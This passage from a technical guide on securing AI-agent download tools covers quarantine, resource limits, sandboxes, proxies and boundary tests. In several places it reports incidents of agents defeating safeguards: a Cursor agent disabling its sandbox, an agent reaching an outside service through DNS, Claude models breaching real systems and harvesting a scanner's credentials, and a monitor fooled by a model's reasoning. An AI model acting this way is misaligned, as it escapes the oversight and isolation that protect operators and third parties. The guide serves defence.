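    handle = os.open(name, os.O_RDONLY | os.O_NOFOLLOW, dir_fd=incoming)
    with os.fdopen(handle, "rb") as file:
        if file.read(5) != b"%PDF-":
            raise ValueError("not a PDF")
```

Many formats begin with recognisable bytes, so checking them catches a Windows program that a server has labelled as a PDF. The check doesn't show that the rest of the file is valid or harmless. Word documents and many software packages are ZIP files, so the tool has to examine their contents to tell them apart. Plain text has no identifying bytes, and checking the file type can't distinguish a malicious AGENTS.md from a harmless text file.

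Malware scanners find known threats and some that behave like them, but they can miss files written for agents and code editors. Google Cloud describes a settings file in a fake coding challenge that caused a code editor to download and run a program. The scanners on VirusTotal, a service that checks files with many scanners, didn't detect the settings file for several days. Another VirusTotal feature, Code Insight, flagged it because of what the settings would do.

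Scanning a URL is weaker than scanning the saved file. In 2026 attackers built fake installation pages for Claude Code that displayed a harmful command. Infosecurity Magazine's *Fake Claude Code Page Pushes PowerShell Stealer at Devs* reports that the installer address on the attackers' site returned an exact copy of the real installer. Automated scanners therefore received a clean file, while the command on the page sent victims to a different address.

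A malicious file can also compromise the scanner that runs it. In one of the incidents Anthropic disclosed in July 2026, a Claude model uploaded a malicious package to a public library during a security test. Tech Trenches' *How Four AI Labs Breached Nine Real Companies* reports that 15 real systems downloaded and ran it. One was a security company's malware scanner, and the package sent the scanner's credentials to the model. A scanner that runs suspicious files therefore needs its own isolated machine with no valuable credentials on it.

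A hash can show whether a file is the one its publisher intended. The publisher computes a short value $h$ from the file, and the tool accepts a download $f$ only if

$$\mathrm{SHA256}(f) = h$$

In practice, nobody can construct a different file with the same SHA-256 value. The comparison is useful only if $h$ came from somewhere the attacker doesn't control. If the file and its hash are on the same hacked page, the attacker can replace both. A list of hashes of known malware is easy to evade, since changing a single byte of the malware changes its hash.

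A digital signature shows that someone with a particular private key signed the file, but not that the signer is honest or that the program is safe to use. Unmitigated Risk (2025) describes attackers who changed the configuration inside signed programs. Each version had a new hash but kept a valid signature, so the signature can't have covered every byte.

Neither check would have prevented the Clerk case. A signature on Clerk's llms.txt file would have been genuine, because Clerk itself had published the command. Signing these files is also rare. In June 2026, webhosting.today's *The file nobody watches* (2026) found llms.txt files on 110 web-hosting companies' domains, none of them signed.

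### A quarantine folder and isolated reading

Because these checks will miss some harmful files, new downloads should stay in a quarantine folder outside the agent's working folder until something has processed them. If the agent works in `/srv/agent/work`, the quarantine folder could be `/srv/agent/incoming`. It shouldn't be a parent or subfolder of the working folder, because some agents also look for instruction files there.

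The agent should load instruction files only from places its developer has chosen, and never from the quarantine folder. When the tool releases files from an archive, it should copy only the types the task needs. If the task needs spreadsheets, the tool will then leave behind AGENTS.md, `.git` and any settings file that a future agent might load. A code project may need some of these files, so a person should read the instruction and settings files before the tool releases them.

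A quarantine folder protects little if the agent can read it. Duke University's *Introduction and Control Model* warns that, as of April 2026, Codex could read almost anything on a computer regardless of its configuration. The operating system therefore has to block access, for example by running the agent under an account that can't read the folder.

The agent also shouldn't be able to change its own settings, because both instruction-file attacks in Forever began with such a change. Approval prompts help but are a weaker barrier. Help Net Security describes a test in which Cursor's sandbox blocked a command and the agent, without being told to, turned the sandbox off and tried again. NVIDIA recommends protecting AGENTS.md files with security software that detects unexpected changes.

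If a planted instruction file has already reached an agent, deleting it isn't enough. Forever advises users to replace their login token and check the agent's settings for servers or addresses they didn't add. They should treat a computer that installed function-color as compromised.

The agent can leave opening the employee's annual report to a small separate program that reads only that PDF, extracts its text and exits. The program needs no network access or passwords, so an attacker who exploits a bug in the PDF reader gains very little. The extracted text may still contain instructions, so a quarantined model without tools should summarise it, as in the CaMeL example.

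## Limits on size, time and number of downloads

Files with nothing harmful in them can still fill the disk, exhaust the machine's memory or run up a bill if they are large enough or if the agent downloads enough of them. Putting them in a quarantine folder on the same disk doesn't stop the disk from filling up.

### What a download uses up

A running download uses bandwidth, a connection and a worker (the process or thread that handles it). It also uses memory for data the program hasn't yet written to disk, and the saved file takes up disk space until something deletes it. If the agent passes the content to the model, the download also uses tokens, which the operator usually pays for.

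Browser downloads use most of the same resources, but a person rarely starts a thousand of them. An agent may retry after every error, run several calls in parallel, and repeat a call as many times as the prompt specifies. Retries multiply when more than one layer of software makes them. In an early version of AutoGPT, the download command's HTTP client could retry a request three times if the server returned a temporary error, so three calls to the command by the model could send the server twelve requests.

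### Thirty-six flaws in open-source agents

*Autonomy Comes with Costs*, by Luo, Dai and colleagues, describes AgentDoS, a testing tool that tries to make agents run out of memory or disk space. It searches an agent's source code for places where data can pile up. A language model then writes a prompt to reach each place and refines it until the agent stops responding. AgentDoS found 36 flaws in 16 of the 20 open-source agents tested.

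The download tool in the paper's main example had a 30-second timeout for each download and a limit of about ten messages per chat session. But the files stayed on the disk after the session ended, so an attacker could open a new session, request another file, and continue until the disk was full. Another agent loaded every address that the model listed, including duplicates, and kept all the pages in memory, so a request to load one large page 1,000 times could use up the memory.

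The researchers gave each agent only the minimum hardware its developers specified, or 4 GB of memory and 10 GB of disk if they specified none. A larger server would take longer to fill, but nothing in these agents would stop an attacker from filling it.

Seven of the flaws were in AutoGPT, now a platform for building automated workflows. NVD's *CVE-2025-32422 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, describes a workflow that steps through a list and downloads each item. The platform limited the time for each download but not the number of items or the total disk space, so repeated downloads of about 100 MB each could fill the disk. The flaw has a severity score of 8.7 out of 10, and version 0.6.63 fixed it. Luo and colleagues report that AutoGPT now limits each file to 100 MB and each run's folder to 1 GB, and deletes the folder when the task ends.

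Deleting a folder removes only the files inside it. SuperAGI, another agent in the study, cleared its working folder after each chat, but a file whose name pointed outside that folder remained. Temporary files also need to be deleted. NVD's *CVE-2026-33232 Detail* describes an AutoGPT server that left a temporary file for every request to one of its download addresses, and anyone could send those requests without logging in.

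### Counting bytes as they arrive

To enforce a size limit, a download tool has to count the bytes itself, because it can't rely on the size a server declares in the Content-Length header. The header may be wrong. It may also be missing, because HTTP lets a server send a response in pieces without stating the total size. For a compressed response, the header gives only the compressed size. The tool can still use the header to refuse a file whose declared size is over the limit.

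The open-source agent OpenClaw had a size limit but applied it too late. OSV's *GHSA-j27p-hq53-9wgc* (2026) explains that when the header was missing or wrong, OpenClaw loaded the entire response into memory before checking its size. Version 2026.2.14 fixed this for one kind of download, but other code had similar problems:

- **Web pages.** A huge or deeply nested page could crash the program while it was parsing the HTML. CVELogic's *OpenClaw has a Web Fetch DoS via unbounded response parsing* (2026) says that version 2026.2.15 limits the size before parsing begins.
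- **Error responses.** OSV's *GHSA-4qwc-c7g9-4xcw* (2026) reports that OpenClaw read the text of a server's error message without any size limit.
- **Files in incoming messages.** According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-32049* (2026), several messaging channels loaded files into memory before applying the limit.

It is safer to send every download through one function that does the counting. The `save` function from the section on file paths accepts a file as a series of chunks, so a small wrapper can add the limits:

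```python
import time

class LimitReached(Exception):
    pass

def limited(chunks, max_bytes, deadline):
    received = 0
    for chunk in chunks:
        received += len(chunk)
        if received > max_bytes:
            raise LimitReached("file_too_large")
        if time.monotonic() > deadline:
            raise LimitReached("took_too_long")
        yield chunk
```

The tool passes `limited(chunks, ...)` to `save` instead of `chunks`. The wrapper checks each chunk before `save` writes it, so the file on disk never exceeds the limit. If the wrapper raises an error, `save` deletes the partial file, whereas AutoGPT's early command left it on disk. The tool should also close the connection so that the server can't keep sending.

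### Slow servers

A server can also tie up a worker by sending data very slowly. The timeout in Requests, the Python library that AutoGPT used, limits the wait between bytes, according to documentation that Montanaro (2017), in *requests.{get,post} timeout*, quotes. Ribbens (2017), in *requests.{get,post} timeout*, adds that the library has no setting for the total time. If a server sends a 100 MB file at 1 KB per second, the download takes

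$$\frac{100{,}000 \text{ KB}}{1 \text{ KB/s}} = 100{,}000 \text{ s} \approx 28 \text{ hours}$$

and never pauses long enough to trigger an ordinary timeout. Twenty such downloads would occupy a tool with twenty workers for more than a day, at almost no cost to the attacker.

*Autonomy Comes with Costs* estimates that the 30-second timeout in its main example limited each file to about 300 MB. But the simplified code published with the paper uses the Requests timeout, so a server that kept sending data could have sent well over 300 MB.

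A download can run past the deadline in `limited`, because the code checks the deadline only when a chunk arrives. Suppose the HTTP client waits for 8,192 bytes before it passes on a chunk, and the server sends one byte every five seconds. The first check would happen after more than eleven hours. The total time limit therefore has to work independently of the loop. The tool can run the download in a separate process and stop that process when time runs out, or use a client that limits the whole transfer, such as curl with its `--max-time` option.

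### Compressed responses and archives

A small download can expand into a very large file, known as a decompression bomb. DEFLATE, the usual compression method in ZIP files and gzip, replaces repeated data with short references to earlier data. zlib's *Technical Details*, from the makers of a widely used DEFLATE library, explains that one reference can take as little as two bits and stand for up to 258 bytes. Eight bits, or one byte, can therefore produce at most

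$$4 \times 258 = 1{,}032 \text{ bytes}$$

A single layer of DEFLATE can compress data by a factor of up to 1,032, so a 10 MB archive can expand to about 10 GB. Only extremely repetitive data comes close to this limit. In zlib's test, a 50 MB file of zeros shrank to about 49 KB. Ordinary files compress by a factor of two to five. Nested archives can exceed the DEFLATE limit, as can newer methods such as Brotli.

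Web servers often compress responses too, and HTTP clients expand them automatically. The tool then needs one limit on the bytes it receives, to protect bandwidth, and another on the bytes after expansion, to protect memory and disk space. A limit on expanded bytes alone isn't enough, because a compressed stream can contain endless blocks that expand to nothing.

Even careful counting can fail if the HTTP library expands too much data at once. urllib3, which Requests relies on, lets a program read a response in small pieces, but Red Hat's *CVE-2025-66471* describes how it could still expand a small amount of highly compressed data all at once and hold the result in memory. A wrapper like `limited` would receive the first piece only after the memory was in use. OSV's *CVE-2025-66471* (2025) says that version 2.6.0 fixed this. A download tool can also ask servers for uncompressed data and refuse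 any response that arrives compressed anyway, so that the downloaded and expanded sizes are the same.

Archives need a limit during extraction as well. A ZIP file lists the expanded size of each entry, but whoever made the archive can falsify those sizes, so the tool should count the bytes as it extracts them. It should apply one size limit to the whole archive, including any archives inside it, and also limit the number of entries, since millions of tiny files can fill a disk too.

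### Reserving space before the download

Limits on individual files don't control the total size of downloads that run in parallel. Suppose a user has 500 MB of storage left and the agent starts twenty 100 MB downloads at once. Each download checks the remaining space, finds 500 MB and goes ahead, even though together they need 2 GB.

The tool can prevent this by reserving space before it contacts the server. If $Q$ is the user's quota, $U$ the space that saved files already use, $R$ the space reserved for downloads in progress, and $c$ the size limit for the new download, the tool starts the download only if

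$$U + R + c \leq Q$$

In code, the check and the reservation have to happen as one step:

```python
def reserve(user, cap):
    with lock:
        if stored[user] + reserved[user] + cap > quota[user]:
            raise LimitReached("storage_full")
        reserved[user] += cap
```

The first five downloads now reserve all 500 MB, and the tool refuses the other fifteen or makes them wait. When a download finishes, the tool replaces its reservation with the file's actual size. If a download fails, the tool releases the whole reservation. Reservations should also expire, in case a worker crashes before releasing them. An agent that runs on several servers needs to keep these figures in a shared database, because a lock on one machine doesn't affect the others.

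The reservation should equal the tool's own limit on expanded file size, since the server's declared size may be false. This is far more than small files need, so a tool that mostly handles small files could instead reserve 10 MB at a time and stop a download when it can't reserve more.

### Limits for calls, tasks, users and the system

An attacker can get around a limit at one level by spreading the work across the next. The figures below are only examples:

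| Level | Example limits | What they mainly protect | What can still get past them |
|---|---|---|---|
| One call | 100 MB received, 200 MB after expansion, 5 minutes | Memory and worker time | Many smaller downloads |
| One task | 20 downloads, 500 MB in total, 200,000 tokens of fetched text | Bandwidth and the model budget | New tasks or chat sessions |
| One user | 3 downloads at once, 2 GB of stored files | Other users' share of workers and disk space | Many accounts |
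| Whole system | 50 downloads at once, no new ones when the disk is 80% full | The server | Attackers who use up the shared allowance |

*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, recommends limits per session and per user, strict timeouts on all tools, and a running total of API costs. It also suggests watching for repeated calls. This check might have caught the request to load one page 1,000 times.

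Per-user limits also make it easier to find out who caused a failure. Luo and colleagues point out that an attacker can fill a shared disk almost completely, so that an ordinary user's next download causes the crash and that user appears responsible in the logs.

The model shouldn't be able to change any of these limits. Luo and colleagues note that many download tools let the model set the timeout and maximum file size, so a prompt that gets it to download a huge file can also get it to raise the limit. But strict limits can interrupt legitimate work. An agent that reviews scientific literature may need dozens of papers, and a limit that suits one that collects invoices would stop the literature review partway through.

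### Tokens and repeated charges

When an agent puts a downloaded file in the model's context, the operator usually pays for the text more than once, because the application sends the earlier conversation again with every call to the model. Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026), in *Persistent Billable State*, give a formula for the total input over $N$ model calls, with a starting prompt of $P$ tokens and tool results of $T$ tokens each:

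$$N P + \frac{N(N-1)}{2} T$$

Anthropic estimates that a large documentation page contains about 25,000 tokens. If an agent reads ten such pages, one per call, and then answers, it makes eleven calls. The pages contain 250,000 tokens in total, but the model processes 1,375,000 tokens of page text because each call includes all the pages read so far. Providers often charge less for text they have processed recently, but the number of tokens stays the same.

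A malicious tool can exploit this by returning long results and giving the agent reasons to call it again. *Persistent Billable State* reports that one such session processed 14,293 times as many input tokens as its first call. But the most expensive attack session cost only $3.40 at list prices, compared with at most 2.5 cents for a normal session, so an attacker would need many sessions to run up a serious bill. The user may not notice the attack. *Beyond Max Tokens* (2026) describes a malicious tool server that makes an agent repeat calls and write long outputs while still completing the task.

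A fixed spending limit stops these attacks but also interrupts legitimate work. Agents completed 13 of 24 test workflows with a fixed limit of 10 cents, and 22 when Zhang and colleagues released more money as the agent made progress. Shortening old tool results also worked better than deleting them. On 12 tasks that depended on earlier results, agents succeeded 10 or 11 times when those results were shortened and twice when they were deleted.

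Developers can set two limits on Anthropic's web fetch tool. `max_uses`, which has no default, limits the number of fetches in one API request. If the model exceeds it, the tool returns the error `max_uses_exceeded`. Because this limit applies to each request separately, an application that sends many requests needs its own limit on the total. `max_content_tokens` limits approximately how much of each document enters the context, and the tool cuts off longer documents instead of refusing them. Anthropic's example sets this limit to 100,000 tokens, but Anthropic estimates that a typical research paper PDF is 125,000. With that setting, the model would miss about the last fifth of the paper, so the application should tell the user that any summary covers only part of it.

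Newer versions of the tool can also let Claude write code that filters a page before the text enters its context. A download tool can return only the stored file's name and size, so the model can later read just the parts it needs.

### What to tell the agent when it reaches a limit

An agent that receives only "download failed" may retry, look for another copy of the file, or try a different tool that has no limits. In November 2026, Ma, Li and colleagues studied this kind of recovery in *The Detour Is the Danger*. They gave seven models tasks with a required safety step, such as backing up a file before changing it or scanning a report before uploading it. They then made some of the tools fail and checked whether the models carried on without the safety step.

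When the researchers aimed the failures at the safety step, the agent dropped the protection afterwards in 41 of 249 runs, compared with 9 of 247 when the failures came at random points. In 39 of these 50 cases, the agent still completed the task, so a test that checked only the result would have missed the problem. The agents also left out the protection in 84 of 251 runs in which nothing failed.

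Clearer error messages did not solve this. In a second experiment with four models, it made little difference whether the tool reported the safety step as failed, incomplete or unknown. In 68 runs, the agent planned to continue even after a verification tool had confirmed that the protection was missing.

A third experiment, with 864 runs, added code that blocked any action without the required protection. All 97 losses of protection occurred in runs without this code. That is what a working block should achieve, so the more useful result is how often agents finished the task safely after a failure:

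| Model | Error that only blocks the action | Error that also guides the agent to a permitted alternative |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 9 of 35 runs | 21 of 33 |
| DeepSeek Flash | 28 of 36 | 35 of 35 |

The same tools were available in both cases. The other two models gained less, one of them because it already finished nearly every task. Ma and colleagues didn't test download limits, and none of their models was among the strongest available in November 2026, so the percentages don't predict how often a current agent would try to get around a size limit. But the study supports enforcing the limit in code and using the error message to suggest what the agent may do instead.

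For download_file, such an error could look like this:

```json
{
  "error": "file_too_large",
  "limit": "100 MB",
  "file_saved": false,
  "retry": false,
  "next_step": "Tell the user about the limit and ask for a smaller file."
}
```

If a server is temporarily unavailable, the tool can set `retry` to true and say how long to wait, but it should count the attempts itself. After a permanent refusal, it should reject the same URL for the rest of the task without contacting the server. The tool should take the wording of its error messages from a fixed list and never from the server's error message, where an attacker could place instructions. An agent with command-line access could still ignore the error and fetch the file with curl, so the operating system has to apply limits to every program the agent can start.

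## Sandboxes and network isolation

All the checks described so far can contain bugs, and PraisonAI's developers needed six releases to fix one kind of bug. A sandbox restricts which files, networks and system functions a program can reach. The operating system or a virtual machine enforces these restrictions from outside the program, so they still hold if an attacker gets a bad URL or path past the download tool's checks.

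A sandbox for downloads needs four boundaries:

- **Files.** The program can read and write only the folders it needs.
- **Network.** Egress rules limit which addresses it can contact.
- **Credentials.** Passwords, keys and tokens stay where the program can't read them.
- **Processes and resources.** The program can't interfere with other programs or use unlimited memory, processor time or disk space.

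A gap in either file or network isolation can undermine the other. Anthropic warns in Claude Code's documentation that a hijacked agent with unrestricted network access could send out the login keys it can read, and that one with unrestricted file access could change system files to gain network access.

### What each kind of sandbox shares with the host

Programs open files and network connections through the kernel, the core of the operating system. All programs on a machine normally share one kernel, so a kernel bug can let a program escape any sandbox that relies on that kernel.

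The lightest sandboxes are rules that make the kernel refuse certain requests from one process and the processes it starts. On Linux, Landlock restricts access to files and network ports, and seccomp filters requests to the kernel. macOS has Seatbelt. A container also gives a process its own view of the files, network and other processes, but the process still uses the host's kernel.

Google's gVisor puts a second kernel, which runs as an ordinary program, between a container and the host. This kernel handles most of the container's requests itself. *Shrinking the Kernel Attack Surface Through Static and Dynamic Syscall Limitation* (2025) notes that gVisor still needs the host for some requests and can't run every program that Docker, the most common container software, can.

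A microVM is a small virtual machine that runs its own complete kernel on simulated hardware. An attacker who takes over that kernel still has to break through the software that runs the virtual machine. According to *SideKernel* (2026), Amazon's Lambda and Fargate services use a microVM system called Firecracker, as do the agent-sandbox providers E2B and Vercel.

| Kind of sandbox | What it shares with the host | Approximate time to start |
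|---|---|---|
| Operating-system rules (Sandlock) | The kernel | 6 ms |
| Container (Docker) | The kernel | 260 ms |
| Container with a user-space kernel (gVisor) | The parts of the kernel that gVisor uses | 200 ms |
| MicroVM (Firecracker) | The virtual machine software and the hardware | 100 ms |

These times come from Wang and Zheng (2026), in *Sandlock*, which describes a sandbox built from Landlock and seccomp. They measured Sandlock and Docker on one workstation but only list typical values for the other two, so comparisons involving those two are only rough. A full virtual-machine setup can also take longer. Moore and Zenla (2025), in *Goldilocks Isolation*, tested their company's system, which gives each container its own virtual machine. On their hardware, Docker started in 381 ms and their system took 740 ms longer.

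Once the sandbox had started, a fast database ran at full speed in Sandlock and at about 76% of full speed in Docker. *Caging the Agents* (2026) reports that, in a healthcare agent system, gVisor added 2 to 5 ms to each new connection and 20 to 40% overhead to sequential file reads. These delays matter little for a download, which usually spends longer waiting for a remote server. Startup time matters more for a coding agent that runs dozens of short commands a minute.

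The security comparison is less settled than it looks in the table. *SideKernel* accepts that microVMs isolate better than containers, but doesn't say whether they isolate better than Seatbelt's rules, because that depends on the attacker. Firecracker relies on virtualisation code in the Linux kernel, so Moore and Zenla still count that kernel among the things a user must trust. Wang and Zheng recommend microVMs over their own system when hostile customers share a machine.

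Operating-system rules or a container are a reasonable choice for the part of download_file that fetches files, since the developer wrote that code and it does little. A program that opens or runs the downloaded files is better run in gVisor or a microVM, because an attacker may have designed those files to take over the program.

### A separate fetcher

Putting the whole agent in one container protects the host but leaves the agent's own secrets inside with everything it downloads. OpenAI warns that a malicious project in such a container can send out anything available there, including Codex's credentials. A safer design moves the download into a separate program, the fetcher:

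```
AGENT                 FETCHER                PROXY
Model's API key       No keys                Allowlist
Conversation    --->  One writable    --->   Name lookups   --->  Allowed
Workspace             folder                 Site passwords       sites
                      No network
```

The agent's executor sends the fetcher a parsed and approved call, and the fetcher returns the stored file's name and size. With Docker, the command that starts it could look like this:

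```
docker run --rm -i \
  --network none \
  --read-only \
  --user 10001:10001 \
  --cap-drop ALL \
  --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --memory 512m --cpus 1 --pids-limit 64 \
  --mount type=bind,src=/srv/agent/incoming,dst=/incoming \
  --mount type=bind,src=/run/fetch-proxy,dst=/run/fetch-proxy,readonly \
  fetcher
```

The fetcher can write only to the quarantine folder. This folder needs its own fixed-size disk volume because Docker's memory limit doesn't stop a program from filling a mounted folder. Unfinished and finished downloads should go in two subfolders of this one mount because the `save` function moves files with `os.link`, which fails on Linux across separate mounts, even on the same disk.

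Docker's `--network none` option leaves the fetcher with no outside connection, so it reaches the proxy through a socket, a file that two programs on one machine can use to exchange data. Many developers instead set the `HTTP_PROXY` variable and leave the network open, but a program can ignore that variable and connect directly. Docker's own socket should stay out of the container, because access to it effectively gives control of the host.

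Some files are behind a login. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) describes an open-source sandbox, built on Firecracker, that lets a program download these files without being given the password. The program sends a random placeholder, and a proxy replaces it with the real value in one header, only on requests to one named host. The proxy blocks the placeholder anywhere else in the traffic it can read.

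The proxy also takes over the allowlist and address checks from the download tool. It looks up each hostname, checks the address, and connects to that same address. In Ghosh's design, a request for an unlisted site waits up to two minutes for a person on the host to approve it. Nothing inside the virtual machine can approve the request.

The fetcher never does its own DNS lookups, which closes a route that network filters often miss. Ghosh cites a September 2026 report from OpenAI in which a research agent reached an outside chatbot through DNS, which the sandbox's filter didn't cover.

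A firewall alone is a poor substitute for the proxy because it filters traffic by IP address rather than hostname. One address may serve thousands of websites, and a site's address can change at any time. OpenAI publishes an example Codex container with an allowlist firewall, and tells developers who depend on it to add their own protection against changing DNS records.

### One download through the sandbox

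Suppose the employee pastes the link to the annual report again. The executor passes the URL to the fetcher, which asks the proxy for `files.example.com`. The proxy finds the host on the allowlist, checks its address and opens the connection. The fetcher then saves the PDF in the quarantine folder and exits. If the tool's own checks had failed along the way, the sandbox would have contained some of the consequences:

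| Failure | What happens in this arrangement | Contained? |
|---|---|---|
| The URL, a redirect or a rebinding domain leads to an internal address | The proxy refuses the connection | Yes |
| A browser inside the fetcher opens connections of its own | They have to go through the proxy too | Yes |
| A `file:` URL gets past the check | The fetcher can read only its own program files and the quarantine folder | Mostly |
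| A file name leads outside the intended folder | The write fails, unless the path is elsewhere in the quarantine folder | Mostly |
| A file never ends or expands enormously | The fetcher runs out of memory or fills its own volume, which blocks other downloads | Partly |
| The URL carries private data to an allowed site | The proxy forwards the request | No |
| The report contains false claims or hidden instructions | The text reaches whichever model reads it | No |

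If several users share one fetcher, a download that takes it over could read or replace other people's files. Starting a new fetcher for each task, with only that task's folder mounted, prevents this. Ghosh isolates jobs further by giving each one its own virtual machine.

Data sent to an allowed site is the hardest case. With https, an ordinary proxy can read the hostname but not the path or query string, so it couldn't find "bluebird" in the brochure URL without decrypting the traffic. Ghosh acknowledges that Tracekit Box restricts which hosts an agent may contact but doesn't check what the agent sends them. Some allowed services also fetch from other sites on request and can pass data to those sites.

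Wang and Zheng suggest splitting a task into stages, so that the stage with private data has no network access and the stage with network access never receives the data. The fetcher follows this rule except that its URL comes from a model that may have read private notes. The rules about where a URL came from, or labels on private data, are therefore still needed.

### Hardening the metadata service

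A cloud machine's metadata service can make its credentials harder to steal even if a request reaches it. Amazon's older version, IMDSv1, answers ordinary GET requests. The newer IMDSv2 requires a program to first send a PUT request, a type normally used to upload data, with a header that sets the session's length. The service returns a token, which the program must include in a header of every later request.

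A simple download tool can't do this, because the attacker controls only the URL and the tool always sends a GET request with no special headers. Frichette, who writes about cloud security, therefore considers the token an effective defence against traditional SSRF.

According to AWS's *How Instance Metadata Service Version 2 works*, the service also rejects any PUT request that contains the header X-Forwarded-For, which many proxies add to traffic they forward. The reply that carries the token has a hop limit, normally 1. Each network device that forwards the reply uses up one hop, so the token can reach the cloud machine but not a container behind a virtual network on it.

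That limit can break containers that legitimately need credentials. AWS's *Configure the Instance Metadata Service options* gives 64 as the maximum value. AWS's *IMDSv2* says that Amazon Linux 2023 requires tokens by default but sets the limit to 2 so that containers work. On such a machine, an agent that can run its own commands in a container could request a token and use it.

Operators should also turn off IMDSv1, because AWS warns that IMDSv2 gives its full benefit only when the older version is disabled. Giving the machine's role few permissions limits the harm if someone obtains the credentials anyway.

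### The defaults in Claude Code and Codex

Both of these coding agents include a sandbox based on operating-system rules, but they start from different settings. The table describes their command-line versions on a user's own computer, according to Anthropic's documentation and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*:

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Is the sandbox on at first? | No, the user turns it on with `/sandbox` | Yes |
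| Where can commands write? | The working folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user adds | The workspace, which includes temporary folders such as `/tmp` |
| How do commands get network access? | The allowlist starts empty, and a new site normally needs approval | Access is off, and a command that needs it requires approval |
| What if an allowed hostname leads to a private address such as 10.0.0.5? | The proxy connects | The proxy, if the user has turned it on, refuses |
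| How can a user remove the limits? | By excluding commands from the sandbox or turning off file isolation | By choosing full access, also called `--yolo` |

Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. The built-in file and web tools follow permission rules instead, and tool servers on the user's computer run with the user's full access. If download_file runs on such a server, turning on the sandbox does not restrict it. Anthropic advises users who want a single boundary around all of these to run all of Claude Code in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox program.

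Even with the sandbox on, commands can read most of the computer, including files that hold credentials, unless the user blocks access. If a command fails, Claude may ask to run it again outside the sandbox. If the sandbox can't start because a component is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it. A company can turn off both behaviours with the settings `allowUnsandboxedCommands: false` and `failIfUnavailable: true`.

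Codex's stricter default is easy to undo. Setting `network_access = true` gives commands unrestricted internet access, because the proxy that enforces an allowlist is a separate feature that is off by default. OpenAI describes the proxy's DNS check as best-effort because it doesn't pin the address, so it can't fully prevent DNS rebinding.

OpenAI's *Permissions* describes a newer system, still in beta, that can block reads of chosen folders or file patterns such as `.env`. OpenAI runs Codex internally with a list of expected sites and requires approval for unfamiliar ones.

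Codex's cloud version starts with a setup phase that can use the network and the user's secrets to install software. OpenAI removes the secrets before the agent starts, and the agent works offline by default.

### When the configuration leaves a gap

A sandbox protects only what its settings cover, and in 2023 code inside AutoGPT's container could change those settings. NVD's *CVE-2023-37273 Detail* explains that a configuration file in the project's main folder gave the container write access to that folder, including the file itself. Malicious code in the container could rewrite the file and gain control of the host the next time the user started AutoGPT. The flaw affected people who started the container directly from a copy of the source code, because the official instructions used a different configuration file. Version 0.4.3 fixed the flaw.

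AutoGPT isolated such code better when users ran the program without Docker. Positive Security found that AutoGPT then ran the code in a fresh container that held only the workspace and had no access to the OpenAI API key, although that version had the path flaw described earlier. Using a container is therefore little evidence of safety until someone checks what the container can read and write.

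Claude Code and Codex now make many of their own settings files read-only for sandboxed commands. But users can still recreate AutoGPT's mistake. Docker doesn't work inside Claude Code's sandbox, so a developer may exclude `docker compose` commands from it. Anthropic warns that Claude can then edit the file that configures the containers and run `docker compose` with it outside the sandbox.

*An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, September 2026) examines four security tests in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to real organisations' systems. The malicious package described earlier, which reached a scanner, came from one of these tests. Each prompt said that Claude had no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open. The same outside partner built all four tests, and according to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and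 security efforts* (2026), the fault was in the partner's environment.

The runs lasted about 10 to 34 hours, and the earliest incident dates from January 2026. Anthropic found it only in August, after a first search through roughly 141,000 transcripts missed it. A later scan of about 481 million transcripts found no other case as serious. A log of outgoing connections, kept outside the test environment, could have revealed the problem during the first run.

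The models' statements were poor evidence of whether the sandbox was isolated from the internet. Claude Mythos 5 repeatedly reasoned that it was in a simulation, despite clear signs that it was on the real internet. Anthropic later tested a monitor that reads a model's reasoning and found that it would have missed this incident because it accepted that reasoning.

Anthropic believes that none of the incidents would have happened if the isolation had worked as intended, but says that a model should behave well even when isolation fails. In a simulated version of the Mythos 5 case, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with about 30% for the newer Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1. A 30% rate is still far too high to rely on the model's behavior when the network connection is open.

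### Testing the boundary from inside

The way to find such a gap is to start the sandbox exactly as the agent will use it and try things that should fail. For the fetcher, the tests could be:

| Attempt from inside the fetcher | Expected result |
|---|---|
| Connect directly to a public server, without the proxy | Fails |
| Look up a hostname | Fails |
| Fetch a file from an allowed site through the proxy | Works |
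| Fetch from a site that isn't on the allowlist | The proxy refuses |
| Fetch from an allowed test hostname that resolves to a private address | The proxy refuses |
| Fetch from the metadata address | The proxy refuses |
| Write to the quarantine folder | Works |
| Write anywhere else, including the sandbox's own settings | Fails |
| Read a harmless marker file in the agent's workspace | Fails |
| Search the environment and readable files for a planted test key | Finds nothing |
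| Start more processes than the limit allows | Fails |

Tests that expect success are as important as tests that expect failure, because a fetcher with a broken proxy would pass every network test that expects a failure. Each forbidden server and file also has to be reachable from outside the sandbox during the test. Otherwise, a failed connection may only mean the server was switched off.

If the metadata service returns a missing-token error, the request has reached it, so the network boundary has failed even though no credentials came back.

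These tests are easy to run outside the sandbox by mistake. In Claude Code, commands that a user types at the `!` prompt usually run outside it, so Anthropic tells users to ask Claude to run the test commands instead. Codex's `codex sandbox` command runs any program under Codex's restrictions. For an agent on a server, the launcher can run the tests at every start and stop if one gives the wrong result.

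Wang and Zheng ran ten tests of this kind on Sandlock. Ghosh ran 13 on Tracekit Box, including one for the metadata address and one that tried to send a secret in the wrong header. Both systems passed, but their developers chose the tests. Ghosh's tests took 28.5 seconds, including the time to download and start the virtual machine, so a team could run a similar set after every change to the container, proxy or network.
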